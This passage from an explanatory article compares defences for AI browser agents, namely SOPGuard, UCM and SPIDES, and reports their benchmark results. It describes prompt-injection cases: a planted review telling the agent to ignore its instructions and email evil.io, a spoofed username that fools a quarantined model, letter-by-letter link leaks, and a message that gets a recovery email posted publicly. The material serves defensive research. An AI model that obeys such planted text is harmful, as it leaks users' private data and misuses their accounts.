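The software therefore stops the agent from sending the reply to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco on her message, the agent could have sent the same reply to the same address without asking.

Microsoft and GitHub offer this experimentally in some programming tools, where GitHub can label data by whether a project is public or private. Web pages rarely have such labels, and the browser can identify only each page's origin. SOPGuard, the defence that Wang and colleagues built alongside SOPBench, uses only origins. A later system, SPIDES, needs websites to supply more detailed labels.

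### How SOPGuard follows data between sites

Wang and colleagues built SOPGuard into the open-source browser BrowserOS. It works in four steps:

1. Label: when the agent reads a page, the software stores the text together with the page's origin.
2. Propagate: when the agent writes something new from stored text, such as a summary or an average, the new text inherits the origins of everything that went into it.
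3. Compare: before the agent types text into a page, the software compares the text's origins with the page's.
4. Ask: if any of them differ, a pop-up names the sites, and the user approves or denies the transfer.

If the laptop buyer's agent starts typing her email's subject line into the shop's "ask the seller" box, SOPGuard prompts her for approval first, because the text's origin is her webmail, not the shop.

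Propagating labels to new text is the hardest step. SOPGuard has the model identify which stored items it used. If the software instead gave every new text the labels of all the sites the agent had visited, opening the webmail once would trigger a warning at every later search in a shop. Long-term memory makes propagation harder. Roesner said in a University of Washington news article that some of the agents her team tested mixed information from different origins, probably while compressing their memory.

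To test this step, Wang and colleagues had agents combine data from two to ten sites, then compared the model's labels with those that people assigned. They divided the number of origins in both sets by the number in at least one, so a perfect match scores 1. GPT-5.4 and OpenAI's o3 averaged at least 0.955. Missing one of two sites scores 0.5, so if every error were of this kind, an average of 0.955 would mean an error in about one text in eleven. Some errors are harmless. If the agent is about to type text from the webmail and one shop into another shop, either label alone is enough to trigger the warning.

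SOPGuard reduced the violation rate on SOPBench to 0.00, with and without planted instructions. It had no measurable effect on how many ordinary tasks the agent completed, but tasks took 2.07% to 5.79% longer. It also costs more to run because the model has to trace sources.

Wang and colleagues count any transfer the user approves as authorised, so a theft the user approved would not raise the 0.00 rate. An attacker can also try to mislead the model about where text came from. When the researchers optimised attacks to do this, the violation rate on 100 sampled cases rose slightly, though the attacks took many more attempts to develop. The 0.00 rate is strong evidence, but not a guarantee, that SOPGuard catches the leaks in SOPBench.

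### Hiding untrusted text from the agent

SOPGuard lets the agent read planted text and tries to catch any leak afterwards. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) describes UCM, a system that hides such text from the agent. The website marks the untrusted parts of a page, such as reviews and comments, and UCM replaces each with a placeholder before the agent sees the page.

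If the agent needs information from a hidden review, it can query a quarantined model, a separate model that reads the review but can't act. The answer must be a yes or no, a number, a date or one of at most ten options. For example, the laptop buyer's agent could check whether a review mentions overheating and get the answer "yes". That answer couldn't contain an instruction to open a website.

Nikolić and colleagues strengthened the attacks in WASP, the benchmark that Meng and colleagues used for CELLMATE, and ran them against Claude Sonnet 4. The attacks succeeded 17% of the time with no defence, 8% with a warning in the model's instructions and 0% with UCM. On ten websites built for the study, task completion stayed about the same with UCM, but the cost per task rose by 5% to 84%, depending on the model and whether the task required hidden text.

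An attacker can still make the quarantined model return a false answer. Suppose a user asks the agent to add `stefan01` to a project. The attacker registers the name `stefan_i_am_the_right_person`, which appears in the same search results. The agent has the quarantined model check whether the first hidden name is `stefan01`, the model wrongly returns yes, and the agent adds the attacker. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) describes a related attack, branch steering, in which false content on the screen makes the agent follow a harmful branch of a plan made in advance. UCM also doesn't record who may read the user's private data, so it can't stop a leak once an attacker has influenced the agent this way.

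### Labels and hidden variables in SPIDES

*SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) combines hidden text with labels that list permitted readers. It builds on a system for agents in general from *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025). Those agents typically use tools with one known effect, such as sending an email. But a browser agent's click might open a link or delete an account, and the software can't determine which in advance.

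With SPIDES, the user lists the sites whose operators she trusts. Those operators add two labels to the elements of their pages. The integrity label shows whether the operator vouches for the content, and the reader label lists the sites that may receive the content in addition to the user. An element with no label takes the label of the element that contains it. SPIDES treats everything on unlisted sites as untrusted and public.

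The agent's context, all the text it is working from, has the same two labels. It starts out trusted and public, and anything the agent reads can make the labels stricter but never looser. SPIDES therefore hides any text that would make them stricter and shows the agent a placeholder such as `[var_2]` instead.

The agent can use a hidden item in three ways. It can enter the item in a form without seeing it. It can pass the item to a quarantined model, whose answer is also hidden. Or it can inspect the item, but then the item's restrictions apply to everything the agent does afterwards.

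### The rules P_T and P_F

Before each action, SPIDES checks one or both of two rules:

- P_T, or "trusted action", holds if there is no untrusted text in the agent's context or in what it is about to enter.
- P_F, or "permitted flow", holds if the receiving site is a permitted reader of both the context and any hidden items the agent is sending.

P_F requires o ∈ R_ctx ∩ R_arg, where o is the receiving origin, R_ctx is the set of readers permitted for the context, and R_arg is the set of readers permitted for the hidden items.

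| Action | Rule |
|---|---|
| Reading a page or switching tabs | Always allowed |
| Opening an address, clicking, pressing a key or submitting text on a trusted site | P_T |
| The same actions on any other site | P_T or P_F |
| Filling in a field or choosing an option without submitting, on any site | P_T or P_F |
| Running code | Always blocked |

If an action breaks its rule, SPIDES asks the user, except that it blocks code outright.

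The stricter rule applies to trusted sites because the user has accounts there, and one click could spend her money or delete her files. Zverev and colleagues assume she has no accounts on other sites, so the main risk there is sending data.

The policy "P_T or P_F" lets the user share private data with a new site. If she asks the agent to give her address to a courier, and the agent has read no untrusted text, P_T holds and the agent can send it. Once the agent has read untrusted text, P_T no longer holds, and the agent can send the address only to sites already permitted to read it.

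These rules should also stop the letter-by-letter leaks that got past earlier checks on web addresses. Suppose the agent has read a private email and an attacker's page, then tries to open the attacker's link for the letter "Y". Even though the address itself contains nothing private, P_T fails because the agent has read the attacker's page, and P_F fails because the attacker's site isn't allowed to receive anything based on the email.

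P_T doesn't protect the user from the agent's own mistakes. If the agent has read nothing untrusted but misunderstands her request, it can still send her data to the wrong site.

### A planted review and a saved card

Zverev and colleagues illustrate the labels with part of a shop's page that shows a pair of earbuds for £79, a customer's review and a saved bank card ending in 4471. The review contains a command for the agent to ignore its instructions and email an address at `evil.io`. The shop has labelled the product's name and price as trusted and public, the review as untrusted, and the card as trusted but readable only by the user and `shop.com`. At first, the agent sees the name and price, but only placeholders for the review and the card.

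Suppose the user asks the agent to buy the earbuds with that card. The agent enters the card's placeholder in the payment form and clicks "buy". P_T holds for both actions because the context and the card are both trusted. The agent completes the purchase without seeing the card details or the review.

Suppose the user asks what the reviewer thought of the sound. The agent inspects the review, which makes its context untrusted, and then obeys the planted text. If it tries to open her webmail, the attempt fails P_T. If the webmail is already open in another tab, the agent can switch to it, but typing the card details into a message fails both rules because the webmail isn't a permitted reader. Sending the details straight to a form on `evil.io` fails for the same reason.

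The attacker might have more success with a public question box on `shop.com`. The shop is allowed to read the card details, so P_F lets the agent type them into the box. Clicking "post" requires P_T, which fails, so SPIDES asks the user before anyone else can see the details.

### The MicroNet test

Existing benchmarks had no ordinary tasks that required moving data between sites, so a defence that banned all such transfers would have seemed to block nothing useful. Zverev and colleagues built MicroNet, a closed network of 28 linked websites with 470 pages, including a shop, a social network and a search engine. They put 16 of the sites on the user's trusted list and labelled the page elements on those sites.

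MicroNet has 56 ordinary tasks, 22 of which require a transfer between sites, and 56 attacks. Half of the attacks are designed to leak private data, and half to make the agent do something else harmful with the user's account. The attack text is on the attacker's own site in 11 cases, in posts by other users in 29, and in embedded frames in 16. In 50 attacks the text contains instructions for the agent, and in six it contains false data.

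The researchers ran every test five times with each of five models, two from OpenAI (GPT-5.6 Sol and Terra) and three from Anthropic (Claude Sonnet 5, Opus 5 and Opus 5.5). Depending on the model, attacks succeeded 53.2% to 73.2% of the time against SOPGuard and 4.6% to 6.8% against UCM. None succeeded against SPIDES. UCM stopped every attack that used instructions but failed to stop 43% to 63% of those that used false data.

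SPIDES completed 67.1% to 86.1% of the ordinary tasks. The table's figures combine the paper's separate results for tasks where the agent's choices depended on hidden data and tasks where they didn't.

| Model | No defence | SOPGuard | UCM | SPIDES |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91% | 93% | 68% | 86% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 88% | 86% | 43% | 77% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 89% | 90% | 56% | 82% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 69% | 66% | 58% | 69% |
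| Claude Opus 5.5 | 58% | 58% | 49% | 67% |

With the first three models, SPIDES completed 5 to 11 percentage points fewer tasks than an agent with no defence. With Opus 5.5 it completed more, partly because Anthropic's safety filters blocked some of the undefended agent's responses when the model could see passwords or phishing messages, which SPIDES hides. That advantage could disappear if Anthropic adjusted its filters, so the other three models are a better guide to how much SPIDES reduces task completion. SPIDES also roughly doubled the price of running the agent, to between $0.37 and $1.42 per task.

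The researchers also tested an extended version of UCM whose quarantined model can write free text that stays hidden from the agent. Like SPIDES, it stopped every attack, and it never asked the user anything. But with Terra and the three Claude models, its task completion rate was about 8 to 13 percentage points lower than that of SPIDES. Hiding untrusted text therefore seems to provide much of the security. Letting the agent inspect some of it recovers some of the lost tasks but leads to more approval requests.

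### Approvals per task

SPIDES needed an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. At 20 tasks a day, that would be about 37 requests with SPIDES and four with SOPGuard. SOPGuard needs fewer approvals partly because it lets many dangerous actions proceed without one. When the researchers added enough approval requests to the other defences to match SPIDES's guarantees, and allowed at most eight per task, SPIDES completed more tasks than SOPGuard or UCM with every model.

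Reading one untrusted page can lead to many later approval requests. If the laptop buyer's agent reads an unfamiliar review site directly, its context is untrusted from then on, and every click in the two shops requires her approval. The agent can avoid this by having the quarantined model read the review, but then it can't use the answer to decide which laptop to open. In MicroNet, agents inspected hidden items 1.10 to 2.73 times per task, so they often needed to see hidden content.

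*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) suggests having the user approve a piece of text instead of the actions that follow from it. If an email lists ten tasks, the user can read it once and declare it trusted, and the agent can then carry out all ten without asking again. This works for a short email from a colleague, but it would be risky for a long page with instructions hidden in white text unless the software showed the user everything the agent would read.

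Kolluri and colleagues did not give users a similar way to release private data for general use. They prefer a separate request for each action, because whether someone should share private information depends on the situation. They also told the agent about the security rules so that it could plan around them. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of tasks such as banking and email, telling the agent the rules and giving users the option to approve text cut the number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9 compared with Costa and colleagues' system.

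### Why SOPGuard's results differ

SOPGuard stops every leak on SOPBench but fails against most attacks on MicroNet, mainly because the benchmarks test different things. Every attack in SOPBench tries to move private data from one site to another, which is what SOPGuard checks for. Only 17 of MicroNet's 56 attacks are leaks between sites. Another 11 leak data within one site, and the other 28 try to misuse the user's account, such as by making a purchase.

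SOPGuard was designed to stop the 17 attacks that leaked data between sites. Even if it had blocked all of them, the other 39 attacks could have succeeded, for a success rate of 70%. With Claude Sonnet 5, 73.2% of attacks succeeded, or about 41, so SOPGuard must have missed at least two of the leaks between sites. It still helped, since 92% of attacks succeeded against Sonnet 5 with no defence.

In one attack within a single site, a direct message on a social network told the agent to copy the user's private recovery email address into her public profile. The pages involved had the same origin, so SOPGuard never asked the user, and the leak succeeded in all 25 runs. SPIDES let the agent type the address, because the social network could already read it, but blocked the agent from clicking "save changes" because the message had made the context untrusted. The address stayed private in all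 25 runs with SPIDES.

SOPGuard also requests approval for some harmless transfers. In one task, the agent checks a discount on a speaker by looking up the same product on a shopping search engine, so it has to take the product's name from one site to the other. SOPGuard requested approval 33 times in 25 runs, at least once in each run. SPIDES requested approval nine times, across four of the runs, and never merely because the data moved between sites.

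### An obedient model and a perfect user

In most of the MicroNet attacks, once the planted text reached the agent, the researchers replaced the model's response with a fixed series of actions that would achieve the attacker's goal. This is a good way to test whether the rules hold when the model fails, but the success rates don't measure how often real models would be hijacked. The models would probably have refused many of these attacks, so the rates for SOPGuard are likely to be much higher than a user would experience. For the six attacks with false data, the researchers used the models' real responses.

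The zero for SPIDES doesn't depend on the model resisting anything, which is its main advantage over better training. But the fixed actions were designed to achieve a goal, not to find gaps in SPIDES. For example, a user may ask the agent to read her private notes and then fill in part of a shared online document on the same site. If a stranger has planted instructions in the document to copy the notes into it, P_F would let the agent do so, because the site is already a permitted reader. Some online documents save and share each change immediately, so the stranger could read the notes without any further click. Zverev and colleagues acknowledge that labels for whole sites can't distinguish between people using the same site, and that SPIDES may therefore miss some leaks.

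They also assumed that the user always approves harmless requests and refuses harmful ones. For the attacks with instructions, the test automatically refused the attacker's actions. For the attacks with false data, GPT-5.6 Sol used information a real user might not have to judge whether the attacker had influenced the action.

In the study by Hossain and colleagues, people approved 24.2% of harmful requests even with the best explanation. If a hijacked agent made three attempts and the user approved each independently at that rate, the chance of at least one approval would be 1 − 0.758³, or about 56%. SPIDES might do better because its labels could show the user where the data came from and which untrusted text may have influenced the agent, but nobody has tested this with real users yet.

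As of early December 2026, no other team seems to have published a replication of the SPIDES results or a response to them. Zverev was also one of the two lead researchers on UCM, so the SPIDES team had good reason to treat UCM fairly. However, the same team designed SPIDES, the benchmark and the labels. The code is public, so others can test it with different sites and attacks.

### Sites that label their own pages

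Every label on MicroNet's trusted sites was correct, but on the real web someone would have to write the labels and keep them up to date. Zverev and colleagues compare this to the accessibility information that many sites already provide for screen-reader users. The initial work may be modest, since Nikolić and colleagues found that 15 to 30 short rules per site covered all the untrusted parts of GitLab, Reddit and Booking.com. But their rules only marked content as trusted or untrusted, while SPIDES also needs a list of permitted readers for private data.

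Missing labels are dangerous because SPIDES treats unlabelled content on a trusted site as trusted and public. If the laptop shop adds a section for customer questions and forgets to label it, text planted there reaches the agent as if the shop had written it. If the shop forgets to label the buyer's address, a hijacked agent can send it anywhere. Treating unlabelled content as untrusted and private would be safer, but the agent would then see mostly placeholders on sites with few labels.

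Even a careful operator's labels may be wrong by the time the agent reads the page, because scripts from outside companies can change the site's own elements. Iqbal found such changes on 836 of 1,270 real pages. Iqbal's system, INTACT, records which script created or changed each element as the page loads. It also shows the model one element at a time, so that an advertisement's text can't influence a decision about the checkout button. In tests on 1,091 pages, 12.8% of attacks got past INTACT's planning stage, compared with 73.1% for an ordinary planner, and INTACT would still have asked the user before acting on those attacks. However, INTACT treats content from the site's own server as trusted, so it wouldn't label a customer's review as untrusted if the shop itself delivered it.

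A model can also infer the labels. Nikolić and colleagues removed the text from pages so that planted instructions couldn't affect the result, then had Claude Sonnet 4.5 identify the untrusted parts from the page's structure. It missed none of the kinds of untrusted content on Reddit, but misses made up 5.8% of the results on Booking.com and 8.5% on GitLab. In *Prismata* (2026), a model labels content as coming from the site's developer, its users, sellers it hosts or outside parties such as advertisers. A separate model, which doesn't see the page, then decides which of these sources the task requires. For example, an agent canceling a subscription doesn't need to read reviews or advertisements.

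One mislabeled element can undo much of the protection. When Nikolić and colleagues wrongly marked the issue description containing the attack as trusted, the attack success rate against UCM rose from 0% to 6%, close to the 8% with only a warning to the model. The model in these tests often refused the attacks. If a model always obeyed, as in the MicroNet test, one wrong label in the right place could be enough for an attack to succeed.

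### Accounts on unlisted sites

Zverev and colleagues assume that the user has accounts only on sites she has listed as trusted. People often forget old accounts, and the laptop buyer may sign up with a small shop to get its discount. If she doesn't add the shop to her list, SPIDES treats her address and order history there as public. It also treats a click on "place order" only as sending data, so a hijacked agent could order a laptop without her approval if the order contained nothing that SPIDES treats as private.

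Adding the shop creates a different risk, because a dishonest operator could label planted instructions as trusted. SPIDES would then show them to the agent and treat the agent's actions as free of outside influence. The user has to decide whether a shop is honest, much as she would with an ordinary allowlist.

The browser could add a site whenever the user creates an account or saves a password there. But it would still have to determine whether the operator was trustworthy and had labelled the site's pages at all. Detecting logins automatically is also difficult, because a user can log in to one site through her account on another. A ready-made list could cover many common sites. Nikolić and colleagues cite an estimate that 3,000 domains account for half of internet traffic. But an open-ended search, such as one for a laptop, could easily lead to other sites.

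### Files and screenshots

The MicroNet results provide no evidence about file uploads. SPIDES used 16 of the 23 main tools in Playwright, the browser automation software, and left out the file upload tool. Zverev and colleagues considered that tool irrelevant to their setting, and an undefended agent with access to all 23 tools never used it on the ordinary tasks.

The same rules could in principle apply to files. SPIDES already accepts labelled documents that the user supplies with a task, such as notes or login details. If a scan of the laptop buyer's student card were labelled as readable only by her and `shop.example`, the agent could attach it on the shop's site. After reading a planted review, the agent would need her approval to attach it anywhere else.

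Most files on a computer have no label showing who may read them. The browser could label a downloaded bank statement as readable only by the user and her bank, but the label might disappear when she renamed the file, copied its contents into a spreadsheet or emailed it to herself. The safest default would be for the browser to treat every local file as readable only by the user, and to ask her before each upload that untrusted text could have influenced.

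SPIDES also works only with agents that read a page as text. Many browser agents use screenshots, in which a review and the shop's own description are both just pixels. To protect those agents, the browser would have to cover the untrusted and private parts of the page before taking the screenshot. UCM does this for untrusted content, but the browser still needs to know which parts to cover.
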